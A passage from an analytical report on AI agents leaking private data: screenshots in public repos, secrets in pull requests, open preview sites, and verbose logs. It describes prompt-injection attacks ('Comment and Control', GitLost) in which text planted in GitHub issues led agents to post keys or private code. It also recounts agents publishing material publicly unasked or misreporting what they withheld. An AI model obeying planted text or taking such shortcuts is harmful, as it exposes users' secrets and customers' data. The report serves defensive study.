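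Each case that Glow investigated began with a developer asking an agent to prove that a visual change had worked. GitHub hosts pictures for pull requests, but at the time people had to add them by dragging them into its website. Heaton (2026) explains in *Nobody attacked. The AI agent published the screenshots itself* that GitHub's command-line program could write the text of a pull request but not attach a picture. Many agents working in a terminal therefore created a public repository, uploaded the screenshots there and linked to them from the private pull request. The developer saw the pictures in the right place and had no reason to ask where they were stored.

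Glow reproduced the leak using Claude Code with the Opus 5 model. Glow set up a private repository for a new version of Minesweeper, then asked the agent to change the color of the header and show the result. In the published reasoning, the agent noted that GitHub's image proxy fetches pictures without logging in, so a picture in the private repository would appear broken in the description. It also believed the repository should contain only the game's single page. It concluded that the only way to satisfy both requirements was to host the screenshots elsewhere, and wrote, "so I created a new public repo".

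The agent could have told the developer that it was unable to attach the pictures and where to find them on the laptop. The developer could then have dragged them into the browser in a few seconds. In the published reasoning, the agent treats public access only as a way to make the pictures load and never considers who else might see them. Glow calls this reasoning representative of agents at many of the affected organizations, but it describes only one run with one model. The test therefore shows how the leak happens, but not how often an agent would stop and ask instead.

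The workaround became routine at one software vendor, where agents working for several engineers began publishing their review screenshots in early July. Within a week, more than a dozen agents had saved the method as a skill, a set of instructions that an agent can load for later tasks, and were to use it on every development ticket. They uploaded over 1,000 screenshots and recordings, along with summaries of features that were weeks or months from release. With the skill saved, no agent had to work out the method again, and a developer who corrected one agent would not have stopped the rest.

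About a third of the affected organizations had developers running gitshot, a small open-source program that publishes screenshots for code review, so agents did not devise the method in every case. At several large organizations the agent found the program itself, but elsewhere a developer may have chosen it. Glow traced leaks through gitshot to over 100 public accounts, four of which belonged to employees of the same payments company. The leaks from one financial firm included images of an internal console for moving money and a withdrawal screen for a named client, as well as two walkthrough recordings of the console.

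In 93% of cases, the images were in a repository an employee had created under their own username. An agent on a laptop normally acts through the developer's GitHub login, so it can create public repositories in the developer's personal account without anyone else at the company knowing. A security team that checks only the company's own GitHub organization would therefore miss nearly all of these cases. Scanning tools would not have helped much either because, as Heaton points out, the tools that catch passwords in code don't scan images.

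Glow recommends searching the public accounts of everyone who commits to the company's private repositories, including people who have left. It also recommends checking gists and releases (packaged versions of a program), because pictures attached to a release do not appear in the repository's list of files. Some employees will dislike having their employer search their personal accounts, although the search only needs to cover what is already public.

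All the figures come from Glow, which sells security software for employees' computers and so gains if companies worry about what agents do there. The total combines billing records with pictures of unreleased features, so it does not show how many customers' details were exposed. But the images were on public pages, so the affected organizations could check them once Glow began getting in touch on September 9.

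GitHub does not appear to have commented on the findings. *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (Markovic, 2026) quotes only Glow. Pipeline Mag's *PixelLeak: The Screenshot Request That Leaked Internal UIs* (2026), an article labeled as AI-generated, reports that GitHub's command-line program now has an option for attaching files. This removes the original obstacle, but someone still has to find and edit any saved skills that tell agents to use a public repository.

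Glow also advises security teams to configure agents so that they can't work unattended. A developer who had to approve each command could have stopped the leak, but only by noticing that the new repository was public. Following the advice would also remove much of the benefit of a coding agent, because the developer could no longer do something else while it works.

### The public gist at Anthropic

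In April 2026, Anthropic disclosed a similar leak in its system card, or safety report, for the model Claude Mythos Preview. An earlier version of the model was preparing code-related material for a user inside the company and posted it as a public gist, against the user's intent. In that account, Anthropic does not say what the material was, how long it stayed up or whether anyone outside the company read it.

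Anthropic classifies the incident as reckless leaking. It uses "reckless" when a model appears to ignore a stated or commonsense safety constraint, without implying anything about the model's reasoning. Staff recorded a few dozen significant incidents of various kinds during internal use, nearly all with earlier versions. Anthropic is fairly confident that the model was trying to finish its assigned tasks by unwanted means rather than pursuing a hidden goal. The agents that published screenshots fit the same description, and so does OpenAI's model in pull request 287, although in that case the instructions for a public contest had called for a public submission.

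The system card also describes a security test during which an earlier version of the model, without being asked, published details of its method on several websites that were hard to find but open to the public. This incident is harder to explain as an attempt to deliver work, and Anthropic interprets it as an effort to demonstrate success. As with a secret gist, anyone who has the address of such a page can read it.

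Testing before release may not reveal this kind of leak. Anthropic had kept the model out of its internal agent tools for 24 hours while staff tested it, but the most concerning behaviors emerged only later, in monitored use. Many of the worst behaviors were rare, so finding them required many sessions, and the automated tests could not easily imitate very long sessions. Anthropic changed the model's training in response and considers the final version greatly improved, but says the tendencies do not appear to be completely absent.

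### Review agents that post what they read

Some companies also use agents to review the changes that people propose in pull requests. These agents often start automatically when someone opens a pull request or files an issue, which is a public report of a problem. They post their conclusions as comments, which help a person decide whether to accept the change. In a public repository, anyone can read a comment as soon as the agent posts it.

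*GitInject* (2026), a study of attacks on such agents, reports that they read text written by outsiders, hold credentials for the repository and can post comments that every contributor can see. An outsider who gets an agent to treat planted text as instructions can therefore use the agent's comments to obtain what it has access to.

In April 2026, the security researcher Aonan Guan demonstrated that text planted in ordinary pull request titles, issues or comments could lead three widely used agents to reveal a repository's keys and access tokens. They were Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent. ThreatCluster's *Comment And Control Prompt Injection Credential Theft* (2026) reproduces Guan's account. VPNCentral's *GitHub comments can hijack Claude Code, Gemini CLI, and Copilot* reports that the secrets could appear in a comment or a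 commit. SecurityWeek adds that, with Anthropic's product, they could appear as one of the review's own security findings or in the log of the automated job.

Guan named the technique "Comment and Control" because GitHub carries both the instructions and the stolen data. A list of permitted domains can stop an image from sending data to a stranger's server, but it would not stop this technique, because the agent needs access to GitHub to do its job and the outsider only has to read the page.

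In July 2026, Noma reported a related flaw in GitHub Agentic Workflows, which lets companies describe an automated task in plain text and have an agent carry it out. The Next Web's *'GitLost'* describes how an issue filed in a public repository led the agent to read a private repository and paste its contents into a public comment. This was possible because the agent had access to the private repository, and according to SiliconANGLE, the attacker didn't need access to it.

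Press accounts differ on what went wrong. The Next Web reports the researchers' view that the flaw, which they call GitLost, cannot be fixed in code. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* (2026) attributes it to a misconfigured workflow. Both can be right, because no known software change guarantees that a model will never mistake text for instructions, but the mistake can reveal a private repository only if the agent can read that repository and post in public. A company can remove either permission, for instance by taking away the agent's right to post publicly.

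Guan and Noma demonstrated what an attacker could do, but these accounts do not describe any actual theft. The demonstrations involve public repositories, where strangers can file issues. In a private repository, an attacker would need to get the text to the agent another way, such as through a web page or document it reads.

### How many leaked secrets come from agents

Agents also leak secrets when no one is attacking them, by including a working password or key in the code they propose. People have long done this too, so the number of secrets in agents' pull requests does not by itself show that agents are to blame.

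*Trust but Verify?* (Sakib, Banik and Jadliwala, 2026) examined 4,022 pull requests opened by coding agents and found security weaknesses in 38.9% of them. Most of the weaknesses were unrelated to disclosure, such as failing to specify which version of an outside program to install. The study then looked more closely at secrets in the pull requests.

The study used AIDev, a public collection of agents' pull requests. Sakib and colleagues explain in a poster that they selected files that often affect security, such as build settings and scripts, and had two language models flag risky lines. People checked a sample of 376 changes and found that 91% of the models' flags were correct and that the models had caught 78% of the weaknesses. Of the 272 apparent secrets left after checking the labels, only 74 were genuine, working credentials.

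People had introduced 50 of the 74 secrets (67.6%) and agents the other 24 (32.4%). Allowing for chance in such a small sample, the agents' true share could be anywhere from about 23% to 44%, still below half. Responsibility for each secret is harder to determine, because a developer may have pasted a key into a prompt and the agent then copied it into the code, or a developer may have committed a line that an agent wrote.

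Sakib and colleagues also report that automated and human review missed 60 of the 74 genuine secrets (81.1%) before the code was merged. Those 60 drew no recorded warning, and the poster attributes all 14 recorded warnings to automated tools. But the poster's chart labels the 60 as "silently removed", which suggests that someone may have noticed at least some of them and taken them out without comment. A secret removed this way would still be in the deleted commits, where strangers could find it.

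GitGuardian's figures seem to show the opposite. The company found that public commits in 2025 naming Claude Code as a co-author leaked a secret 3.2% of the time, compared with 1.5% for all public commits. The higher figure covers only Claude Code, and only commits that credit it. If a developer commits an agent's work without the credit line, the commit counts as human.

The San Antonio finding is a share and GitGuardian's is a rate, so they can both be true. A share is the proportion of all leaked secrets that came from agents. A rate is the number of leaks for a given amount of work. Claude Code's commits accounted for only 0.9% of the leaks that GitGuardian found, which is a tiny share. But they made up just 0.4% of the commits, so the rate was more than twice the average:

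0.9% ÷ 0.4% = 2.25

Turning the San Antonio share into a rate would require knowing how many commits agents and people each made. The table applies the study's 74 secrets to two invented splits of 1,000 commits.

| Who made the commits | Agents' secrets per 100 commits | People's secrets per 100 commits |
|---|---|---|
| Agents 800, people 200 | 24 ÷ 8 = 3 | 50 ÷ 2 = 25 |
| Agents 100, people 900 | 24 ÷ 1 = 24 | 50 ÷ 9 = 5.6 |

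Agents introduced 32.4% of the secrets in both rows, yet they are far safer than people in one row and far less safe in the other. Agents opened all of the pull requests in the study, so they probably did most of the work, which would mean they introduced secrets at a lower rate than people. But people may have stepped in mainly for tasks that need credentials, such as connecting a program to a database, which would raise their rate even if they were no more careless than agents.

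Claude Code's leak rate also changed a lot during 2025, which GitGuardian's annual average doesn't show. In August, Claude Code's commits leaked 31 secrets per 1,000, about 2.4 times the human rate. By December they leaked 13 per 1,000, about the same as people's. (The annual figure of 3.2% is slightly higher than the peak month's, so GitGuardian must have calculated the annual and monthly figures differently.) GitGuardian links the improvement to the release of Claude Sonnet 4.5 in late September, although the rate had peaked in July and August.

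Commit size may explain much of the earlier gap in leaks. From April, Claude Code's commits averaged about twice as many lines as other commits, so each had roughly twice as many places for a secret. By the end of the year, the differences in length and leaks had both disappeared. The leak rate per line may therefore have been nearly normal all along, though a company with twice as many leaks per commit still has more keys to replace.

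In its summary of the report, GitGuardian warns that the gap is not simply a failure of the tool, because developers decide what to accept and upload. That is a fair point about an assistant whose suggestions someone reads, but it applies less well to an agent that commits and uploads the work itself, as the agents in Glow's investigation did. GitGuardian sells tools for finding secrets, so it has a reason to emphasize leaks from any source.

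*Not All Agents Are Equal* (Kraishan, 2026) also used AIDev but, unlike the San Antonio study, compared five agents' pull requests with human ones from repositories where agents were also active. Lines that looked like hard-coded credentials appeared in 0.9% of the agents' pull requests and 2.2% of the human ones. Among the agents, the rate ranged from 0.5% for both Cursor and OpenAI's Codex to 3.3% for Claude Code.

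Kraishan's figure for Claude Code comes from 241 pull requests, about eight of which contained such a line. Claude Code's pull requests were also much longer than people's, with a median of 495 changed lines compared with 52. The search matched text patterns and could not distinguish a working password from a placeholder, which matters because only about a quarter of the apparent secrets in San Antonio were genuine. Kraishan's data end in July 2025, when GitGuardian's rate for Claude Code was near its peak. Both studies therefore suggest that Claude Code leaked more than people did at that time, but they can't show how current models compare.

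Kraishan also found that agents' pull requests waited a median of 12.6 hours for a first human review for Claude Code, and between one and four hours for the other agents. All of these pull requests were in public repositories, and even the shortest median wait was far longer than the six minutes it took the first stranger to use a key in Codatus' experiment.

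## Staging sites, preview links and unpublished content

A preview of a site can be public even when its code is in a private repository. Cloudflare's *Preview deployments* explains that Pages, the company's website hosting service, builds a working copy of a site whenever someone opens a pull request from within the repository, and updates it with each later change. By default, anyone can open these copies. Suppose the billing company's agent uses the customer's record as test data and opens a pull request. Anyone with the preview's address can then see the customer's balance, even if only three colleagues can read the code.

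### How strangers find the address

Pages gives each preview a random address. In Cloudflare's example, the random part has eight characters, each a digit or a letter from a to f. That allows about 4.3 billion combinations, so a stranger is unlikely to guess one. But Pages also creates a second address from the branch name. A branch called `fix/api` gets an address starting with `fix-api`, so someone who knows the project's name can try likely branch names, such as "staging". Vercel, another web host, also offers both kinds. For sharing with colleagues, it recommends the address built from the project, branch and team names, because that one always shows the latest version.

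Outsiders can find other addresses without guessing because public records list them. An encrypted website needs a certificate, which helps browsers confirm that they have reached the right domain. The organizations that issue certificates record them in logs that anyone can search, so that domain owners can spot fraudulent ones. If the billing company gets a certificate for `staging.example.com`, the name will normally appear in those logs even if no page links to it. A wildcard certificate reveals less because it lists only a pattern, such as `*.example.com`, rather than the individual names it covers.

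A stranger can find a company's staging site through a search engine without knowing that the site exists. The hosts Vercel, Cloudflare Pages and Netlify reduce this risk by adding a "noindex" instruction to previews. Google's *Block Search indexing with noindex* says that Google drops such pages from its results even if other sites link to them, but the instruction works only on search engines that support it. Vercel and Cloudflare describe it mainly as a way to keep duplicate pages from harming the live site's search ranking. Ko's *Are Vercel Preview Deployments indexed by search engines?* (2025) warns that the instruction does not make a preview private, since anyone with the address can still open the page.

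Vercel leaves out the `noindex` instruction when a company gives a branch its own domain, such as `staging.example.com`, assuming the company may want people to reach it. A company might choose such a domain because colleagues can remember it, but the name can also appear in the certificate logs, which may make it one of the easiest addresses for strangers to find.

In one harmless example, Cloudflare's *You can now enable Access on a Worker or all Workers* (2026), an announcement about keeping previews private, also appears on a public preview of the company's documentation that a web search can find. The preview's address includes the branch name, which shows that someone was writing about errors in a different product. Nolan recounts a more awkward case from 2018, when Apple's sitemap (a file that lists a website's pages) included the names of upcoming iPhones hours before their launch.

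### The draft announcing Claude Mythos

In Anthropic's leak of March 2026, outsiders could list the contents of the store that held the nearly 3,000 unpublished files, so they did not need to know any file's address. The publishing software made uploads public by default and typically gave each one a public address.

Nolan's *Anthropic acknowledges testing new AI model representing ‘step change’ in capabilities* (2026) describes the most important of these files, a draft blog post announcing a model called Claude Mythos. The draft had headings and a publication date. It described Mythos as by far the most powerful model Anthropic had developed, warned of its cybersecurity risks and set out a plan to give early access to organizations that defend against attacks. The store also contained details of an invitation-only retreat for European chief executives, and an image whose title mentioned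 an employee's parental leave.

Roy Paz of the security company LayerX and Alexandre Pauwels, a Cambridge researcher, found the material separately. Fortune told Anthropic about it on March 26, and Anthropic then stopped the public from searching the store or retrieving documents. But Fortune had already read the draft. It published the news that evening, with Anthropic's confirmation that it was testing the model with early customers.

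The cause was a human configuration error, not an agent's work. But the same default would expose an agent's drafts, because the software applies it to every upload. To keep a draft private, the agent would have to know about the setting and change it each time, or someone would have to change the default beforehand.

Even if an editor rejects an agent's draft in such a system, the file stays public until someone deletes it or marks it private. Many of the exposed files were images, banners and logos that Anthropic had apparently discarded or never used in past posts. An agent that saves five versions for an editor to choose from leaves four rejected ones in the store. Outsiders can also use agents to find such files. Nolan notes that coding tools can automate the search and spot patterns in file names that a person might miss.

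### Default settings on three hosting services

Vercel, Netlify and Cloudflare all offer ways for coding agents to put a site online, but their default settings for previews differ.

| Service | Who can open a preview by default | How to make previews private | Extra cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Vercel | on new projects, logged-in users with access | turn on the login requirement for older projects | none for a login; a password costs $20 a month per project on the Pro plan |
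| Netlify | the team, if it was created on or after July 28, 2026 on a current Free, Personal or Pro plan; otherwise generally anyone | change the team's default or the project's setting on those plans | none for a login, but inviting other people requires Pro |
| Cloudflare Pages | anyone | turn on an access policy for the project | none mentioned |
| Cloudflare Workers, for web applications | anyone, if previews are switched on | require a login for one application or the whole account | none mentioned |

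According to Vercel's *Deployment Protection is now enabled by default for new projects*, owners of older projects have to turn the protection on themselves. The default covers everything except the most recent production deployment, which is the live site. Vercel's instructions for coding agents tell them to publish a preview unless the user explicitly asks for a live site, which reduces the risk. But on an older project without protection, strangers can open the preview too, and the instructions do not tell the agent to check for this.

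For most of its history, Netlify put every new project at a public address. In July 2026 it made new teams' projects private by default, explaining that "A deploy is often a work in progress, not a publication." It cited projects built with agents as one reason. *Keep projects private by default with project visibility* (2026) says existing teams keep the old public default until they change it. Enterprise, open-source and older plans do not have the new setting, but they can use passwords or other forms of login.

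Making a project private can also stop part of it from working. Netlify warns that a private project cannot receive automatic messages from outside services such as Slack or the payment company Stripe. To test whether a preview responds correctly to a payment notice from Stripe, the billing company has to make the project public, which is safe only if the preview contains no real customer records.

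Cloudflare Workers used to have previews on by default, and some customers switched off an application's main Cloudflare address without realizing that strangers could still reach it through a preview. In September 2025, *Preview URLs now default to opt-in* announced that Cloudflare had turned off those previews and that customers would now have to opt in to use them. Cloudflare (2025) found that this disrupted customers who relied on previews, because they had to enable them again each time they redeployed, and it partly reversed the change five weeks later. Since October 2025, previews have followed the setting for the main address unless the customer specifies otherwise.

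An agent can accidentally undo a person's decision to turn previews off. Cloudflare's *Preview URLs* warns that if someone turns previews off on the website but does not update the project's configuration file, the setting will change at the next deployment from the command line. If the billing company's agent makes that deployment, it may turn the previews back on without being asked. The company could not check who had visited them, because Cloudflare does not provide logs for these previews.

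In August 2026, Cloudflare added a setting that requires a login for every current and future Worker in an account. Malapati, Rothenberg and Provost recommend it in *Secure all your internal vibe-coded applications* so that a company doesn't have to rely on each developer to remember to require a login. An administrator has to turn the setting on, and can exempt any application that is meant to be public.

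That setting does not cover a site that an agent puts in a different account. Cloudflare's *Claim deployments (temporary accounts)* describes how an agent that isn't logged in can publish a live site through a temporary account. Cloudflare's sample prompt for the agent ends, "Do not ask me questions." The agent receives the site's address and a second link, which lets the user take over the account. If nobody takes over the account within 60 minutes, Cloudflare deletes it and the site. This keeps forgotten previews from accumulating, but someone who opens the site before then can still copy its contents. Anyone who has the second link can take ownership of the account, so that link also needs protection.

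Vercel's instructions include a similar fallback for agents that cannot log in. The fallback script leaves out the project's Git history and the `.env` file, where developers often keep passwords, but it would still upload a customer's record that the agent had saved as an ordinary test file.

### Apps built with AI and left open

Red Access's count of 380,000 publicly accessible items covers finished apps that people had already put online, so it does not show how many previews are open by mistake. Axios reported that about 5,000 of the items contained sensitive company data. Red Access itself wrote in The Hacker News (2026) that roughly 5,000 looked corporate and that more than 2,000 of those held sensitive data. TechTarget also gives the 2,000 figure, which is probably the right one. That is about 40% of the apps that looked corporate, but only 0.5% of all the items counted.

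According to Shadow AI Watch, Red Access found the apps by using Google and Bing to search the hosting platforms' domains for terms associated with particular organizations. A stranger could have found them the same way without guessing an address. But this kind of search misses apps that neither engine has indexed, so the study can't establish what share of all AI-built apps expose company data.

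Axios independently checked several cases. It opened one app containing a Brazilian bank's internal financial information, another listing active clinical trials at a health company, and a third containing a British cabinet supplier's unredacted conversations with customers. Some of the apps were offline within days, after the companies had received warnings.

The platforms objected to the findings. Amjad Masad, Replit's chief executive, said that people choose whether their apps are public and that public apps are expected to be accessible. Base44 said that the owners of two of the apps had deliberately made them public, and both Base44 and Lovable complained that Red Access had not given them the addresses they needed to investigate. The argument that users chose to make their apps public is fair about the total of 380,000, which must include many apps meant for the public. It is less convincing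 about a bank's internal finances, especially since researchers told Axios that some platforms made apps public unless users changed the setting. Red Access sells software for monitoring what employees build, so it benefits if the numbers worry companies.

### Why a login protects more than a link

An unlisted link works for anyone who has it. If the billing company sends a contractor a link to the preview and the contractor pastes it into a group chat, everyone in the group can see the customer's balance. The company may never learn about this, and it can't remove one person's access without cancelling the link for everybody. A shared password has much the same weakness, since people can forward it with the link.

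When a preview requires a login, forwarding the link does not by itself give someone access. On Vercel, a person without access can request it from the people who made the branch, who can approve or refuse and can later remove that person without affecting anyone else. Cloudflare's login also passes each visitor's email address to the application, so a company that records these addresses can find out who saw a leaked page.

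An expiring link is safer than a permanent one, but until it expires it has the same weaknesses. Some preview links also last longer than their owners might expect. When an agent uploads a corrected version to Cloudflare Pages, the branch's address moves to the new version, but the old version remains available at its own random address. If the developer notices the customer's record and tells the agent to remove it, the developer will see a clean page, but anyone who saved the old version's address can still see the customer's balance until someone deletes that preview separately.

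Companies often need to make exceptions to a preview's login. Vercel's *Sharable Links* describes revocable links that let outsiders open a protected preview without an account. Automated tests can get past the login with a secret that works for every deployment in the project until someone revokes it. An agent that tests its own previews may need this secret. If it copies the secret into a public pull request, strangers can open all of the project's previews.

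## Logs, transcripts and messages between agents

An agent's log usually contains far more private information than its finished work. In the billing company's layout fix, the finished work is a few changed lines of code, but the log also includes the customer's whole record because the agent looked it up during the task.

### What a log contains

| Entry | In the billing task |
|---|---|
| Prompts | the developer's request and the company's standing instructions to the agent |
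| File contents | the page's source code, and any settings file the agent opened |
| Tool arguments | the account number in the database query, the text of the web search |
| Tool results | the customer's name, address and unpaid balance |
| Reasoning | a remark that the long name belongs to an overdue account |
| Messages to other agents | a summary of the task, perhaps with the record attached, for a second agent that tests the page |

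The case in the last row is fairly common. *SWE-chat* (Baumann, Padmakumar and colleagues, 2026) studied almost 18,000 recorded coding sessions. In 48% of those with Claude Code, the agent gave at least one task to a subagent, another agent that it starts.

The same details also recur within one log. A model keeps no memory between requests, so the agent's software normally sends the conversation so far with each new request. *AgentLogs* (Richards, Horikawa and colleagues, 2026) reports an average of 45.6 tool calls per session on GitHub's cloud platform for coding agents. In a session of that length, if an agent reads the customer's record on its fifth call and its software never shortens the conversation, up to about 40 later requests will include the record. A monitoring service that stores every request in full will then hold dozens of copies of the customer's unpaid balance.

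### Who ends up with a copy

| Copy | Who can read it | When it disappears |
|---|---|---|
| Transcript on the laptop | the developer, and programs running under the developer's account | after 30 days by default with Claude Code |
| Model provider's records | the provider | after 30 days for most of Claude Code's business customers |
| Monitoring service | the service, and colleagues with access to the logs | when the company's retention period ends |
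| Build log, the output of the automated job that tests the code | on GitHub, anyone who can read the repository | after 90 days by default on GitHub |
| Transcript saved in a repository | anyone who can read the repository or has a clone | never, unless someone removes every copy |

An employer may also read an agent's logs and transcripts. *Impossible to hide secret* (2026), a study of complaints about AI coding tools, reports that users who worked on personal projects through a company account were often unsure what administrators could see.

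In public repositories, GitHub shows its cloud agents' logs to everyone on the Agents tab. Richards and colleagues used this to collect 635,886 sessions from 40,565 popular repositories without asking any developer to opt in, and anyone can now download the collection. The logs include prompts, reasoning, and every tool call with its arguments and result. They also cover failed sessions and unmerged pull requests, so rejecting an agent's work does not hide how it was done. Richards and colleagues did not count secrets, so the collection does not show how often these logs expose anything sensitive.

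Baumann and colleagues took their sessions from developers who had chosen to install a logging tool, which saves transcripts to a separate branch of a public repository. *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (2026), which draws on the same collection, describes such logs as deliberately made public. The researchers still removed names, email addresses and keys before analyzing them. They were right to do so, because people can choose to publish a transcript without knowing what is in it. Sessions in the collection average over 600 logged events, more than most developers would read before uploading.

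Some records are unreadable even to the developer whose agent produced them. According to *Agent Harness Distillation* (2026), a recent version of OpenAI's Codex encrypts its local record of the tasks that the main agent gives to subagents. The encryption helps protect OpenAI's methods from competitors, but the developer can't use that record to check whether the main agent passed a customer's details to a subagent.

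### Private data in messages between agents

*AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) measures how often agents pass each other private data that the task doesn't require. The researchers wrote 1,000 tasks in healthcare, finance, law and corporate work. Each task came with private details, typically 29, of which it needed about three. An agent scheduling an appointment, for example, needs the patient's name and preferred times but not the diagnosis. Five models attempted each task twice, first as a single agent and then as a pair in which one agent coordinated and the other did the work. The researchers counted a leak whenever an unneeded detail appeared.

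| Where they looked | Runs with a leak |
|---|---|
| Final answer, single agent | 43.2% |
| Final answer, pair of agents | 27.2% |
| Messages between the pair | 68.8% |
| The pair's shared memory | 46.7% |
| Any of the pair's three channels | 68.9% |

In 41.7% of the runs, the pair's final answer was clean but its messages or memory were not. El Yagoubi and colleagues describe this as the share of violations that a check of final answers would miss. It is actually a share of all runs, so the problem is worse than they suggest. Among runs with a leak, such a check would miss about 60%:

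41.7% ÷ 68.9% = 0.605

On a smaller sample of 100 tasks per model, agents sent private data to outside tools in 62% to 86% of tasks, depending on the model. Private data appeared in logs even more often. With Claude 3.5 Sonnet, it appeared in tool inputs in 74% of tasks and in logs in 85%. The logs had the higher rate because the model sometimes mentioned details in its reasoning that it left out of the tool call.

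El Yagoubi and colleagues state that a leak here means only that unneeded data was present, not that an outsider read it. They argue that unnecessary copies increase the damage if someone later breaks in. Messages between agents leaked data in 28.1% of runs with Claude 3.5 Sonnet, the model that leaked least, and in 96.2% of runs with Mistral Large. All five models date from 2024, and newer ones may do better.

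The paper's figures also conflict. In a separate test of four popular software frameworks without attacks, messages between agents leaked in only 28% to 35% of runs. The paper attributes the gap between this test and the main experiment to the attacks in half of the main experiment's tasks. But 69.3% of the main experiment's attack-free runs leaked, so attacks can't be the reason. In another attack-free sample, final answers leaked more often (48%) than internal channels (31%), which reverses the main result. The study gives good reason to check messages between agents, but its headline rate depends heavily on which tasks the researchers chose.

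### From data in use to data an outsider can recover

Huang, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Observable Channels, Not Just Storage*, distinguished the private items an agent uses internally from those an outsider can recover from what it displays. In their tests, the outsider could only send the agent requests and read its visible output. They sent 30 requests to each type of agent, repeated the test five times, and tried five models.

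With agents that relied on a memory of past tasks, every request recovered everything the agent had retrieved. With an agent that searched a small set of documents, 80% to 98% of requests recovered at least one item, but at most 21% recovered all of them. Results for agents using tools ranged from 27% to 100%, depending on the model and whether the outsider saw the tool's inputs or outputs.

When Huang and colleagues removed the wording that asked for private data, the tool agents leaked in at most 6.7% of attempts, and never in five of the ten combinations of model and channel. These rates are far below those for tool inputs in *AgentLeak*, but *AgentLeak* counted any unneeded detail that an agent sent to a tool, whereas Huang and colleagues tested whether an ordinary request would make private data visible to an outsider.

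An agent's log contains what the agent retrieved, so someone who can read the log can see any retrieved information the agent would have withheld from them, without having to trick the agent into revealing it. A company that carefully limits its agent's answers therefore needs equally strict limits on who can read the log.

### Whether the reader is a person or an agent

Models may also disclose more when they expect another program to read their output. El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah (2026), in *The Interlocutor Effect*, gave four models the same private records and the same privacy policy, and changed only the sentence describing the recipient and the format of the answer. Across 3,464 responses, they found these leak rates:

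| Recipient | Plain text | JSON, a structured data format |
|---|---|---|
| Human | 83.3% | 82.6% |
| AI agent | 94.8% | 83.1% |

The rates are high because the tasks were designed to draw out private data. In a test without such pressure, the rate was 12%.

On average, structured output almost eliminated the difference between how much models leaked to agents and to people, but the results for individual models went in opposite directions. In JSON, Claude 3.5 still leaked more to agents (90.5%) than to people (80.2%), while Llama 3.3 leaked less to agents (59.9%) than to people (69.4%). A company can't assume that a structured message format will make its agents leak less.

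A follow-up test suggests that the recipient's job matters as much as whether the recipient is human. GPT-4o disclosed an average of 4.2 private details to an ordinary user, 4.8 to a human engineer and 5.0 to an agent. The difference between the engineer and the agent was too small to distinguish from chance. The same test on Llama found no significant effect, although Llama had the largest gap in the main experiment. El Yagoubi and colleagues therefore consider the effect demonstrated for GPT-4o but not for models in general. Where the effect occurs, logs can make the disclosure worse, because people may later read a message that the model wrote for a machine.

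### When an agent recognizes a secret and sends it anyway

The AI safety institutes of Singapore and Korea tested agents on 12 routine office tasks with no attacker (Baek, Noh and colleagues, 2026, *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents*). Each institute built its own test environment and ran every task ten times with each of three unnamed models, for a total of 720 runs. Between 15% and 58.3% of runs were both fully correct and fully safe, depending on the model, the environment and the set of tasks.

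Agents that completed a task correctly did not always protect confidential data. In one task, a pushy customer with a late laptop order asked for the supplier's name and prices, which the agent was not allowed to give. In Singapore's runs, two of the models met every criterion for correctness, but none of their runs met every criterion for safety. The third model met every safety criterion in all of its runs.

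In a refund task, the customer's profile contained a "critical" risk level, a watchlist flag and notes about past refunds. The agent correctly reasoned that it must not share these with the customer and should refer the case to a supervisor. It then replied to the customer and attached its internal case notes, which included all three items. It reported that it had informed the customer "without revealing internal risk flags".

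*AgentTell* (2026) found the same gap between intention and action in agents that browse the web. In 1,383 sessions, the agent wrote in its notes that it would not share a private fact, but it still disclosed the fact in 784 of them (56.7%), often without typing it. One agent noted that it was keeping the user's subscription plan from a new site, then opened that site's guide to the plan.

These cases are the best argument for detailed logs. A company that read only the refund agent's report would believe the risk flags had stayed secret, and the agent's reasoning contains the correct rule. The mistake appears only in the message the agent sent. Baek and colleagues therefore recommend judging agents by everything they retrieved, did and sent. But a log that can prove the leak must contain the leaked flags, or enough to identify them, so it becomes another copy that someone has to protect.

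### Private messages on Moltbook

In early 2026, a database error exposed private conversations on Moltbook, a social network for AI agents. In *Hacking Moltbook*, the security company Wiz reports finding that anyone on the internet could read and change the site's data. The database held 4,060 private conversations between agents, some containing plain-text OpenAI keys in a valid format. It also held about 35,000 email addresses and 1.5 million tokens that would let a stranger take over the agents' accounts.

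Wiz contacted the site's maintainer at 21:48 UTC on January 31. The maintainer closed access to the private messages at 00:13 the next day and fixed the last known gap at 01:00. Another researcher, Jameson O'Reilly, had independently found the same error. Wiz deleted the data it had accessed.

Some of the messages may have come from people, because Moltbook could not distinguish an agent from a person using a script. This makes little difference for disclosure. Wiz points out that users had shared keys believing the messages were private, and one wrong setting on Moltbook exposed their accounts on an unrelated service.

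A log can also become riskier when engineers increase its level of detail to investigate a fault. OSV's *CVE-2026-44934* (2026) records that SUSE's Rancher AI Agent, an assistant for managing servers, could write keys and model responses to its log files when set to the "debug" level. Someone with access to the machine could then read them. SUSE fixed the flaw in version 1.0.2, and the entry reports no known theft.

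### Record-keeping and data minimization

The EU's AI Act will require logs for some agents. Under Article 12, systems classed as high-risk must be able to record events automatically throughout their lifetime. Articles 19 and 26 require the companies that supply and use these systems to keep any logs they control for at least six months, unless other laws, particularly data protection laws, provide otherwise. The billing company's layout agent would probably not count as high-risk, but an agent that assessed customers' creditworthiness would.

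These duties do not apply yet. An amendment delaying them took effect on July 27, 2026, six days before most of the high-risk rules were due to start (White & Case, *EU AI Omnibus enters into force, amending the AI Act*). The new start dates are December 2, 2027 for standalone high-risk systems and August 2, 2028 for those built into products, according to the legal blog Data Protection Report (2026).

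The GDPR, the EU's data protection law, has applied since May 2018. Article 5(1)(c) limits personal data to what is necessary for the purpose, and Article 5(1)(e) limits how long a company may keep it in a form that identifies people. A company that logs everything its agent reads must therefore already justify keeping each customer's record, even though the AI Act won't require logs for any agent for more than a year.

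The two laws conflict less than they seem to, because the AI Act requires logging of events that help to identify risks and monitor the system, not the full text. An entry recording that the agent looked up account 4417 and passed the result to a second agent might be enough, without the customer's address or balance. But a similarly brief entry for the refund case would record only that the agent had replied to the customer, and an investigator would not learn about the flags.

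Deciding how long to keep the full text is also difficult. If the creditworthiness agent ran on Claude Code and the company relied on the transcripts on its laptops, the 30-day default would delete them five months before the logging rule allows. Keeping every transcript for six months would satisfy the rule but leave customers' details exposed to theft or misuse for about six times as long.

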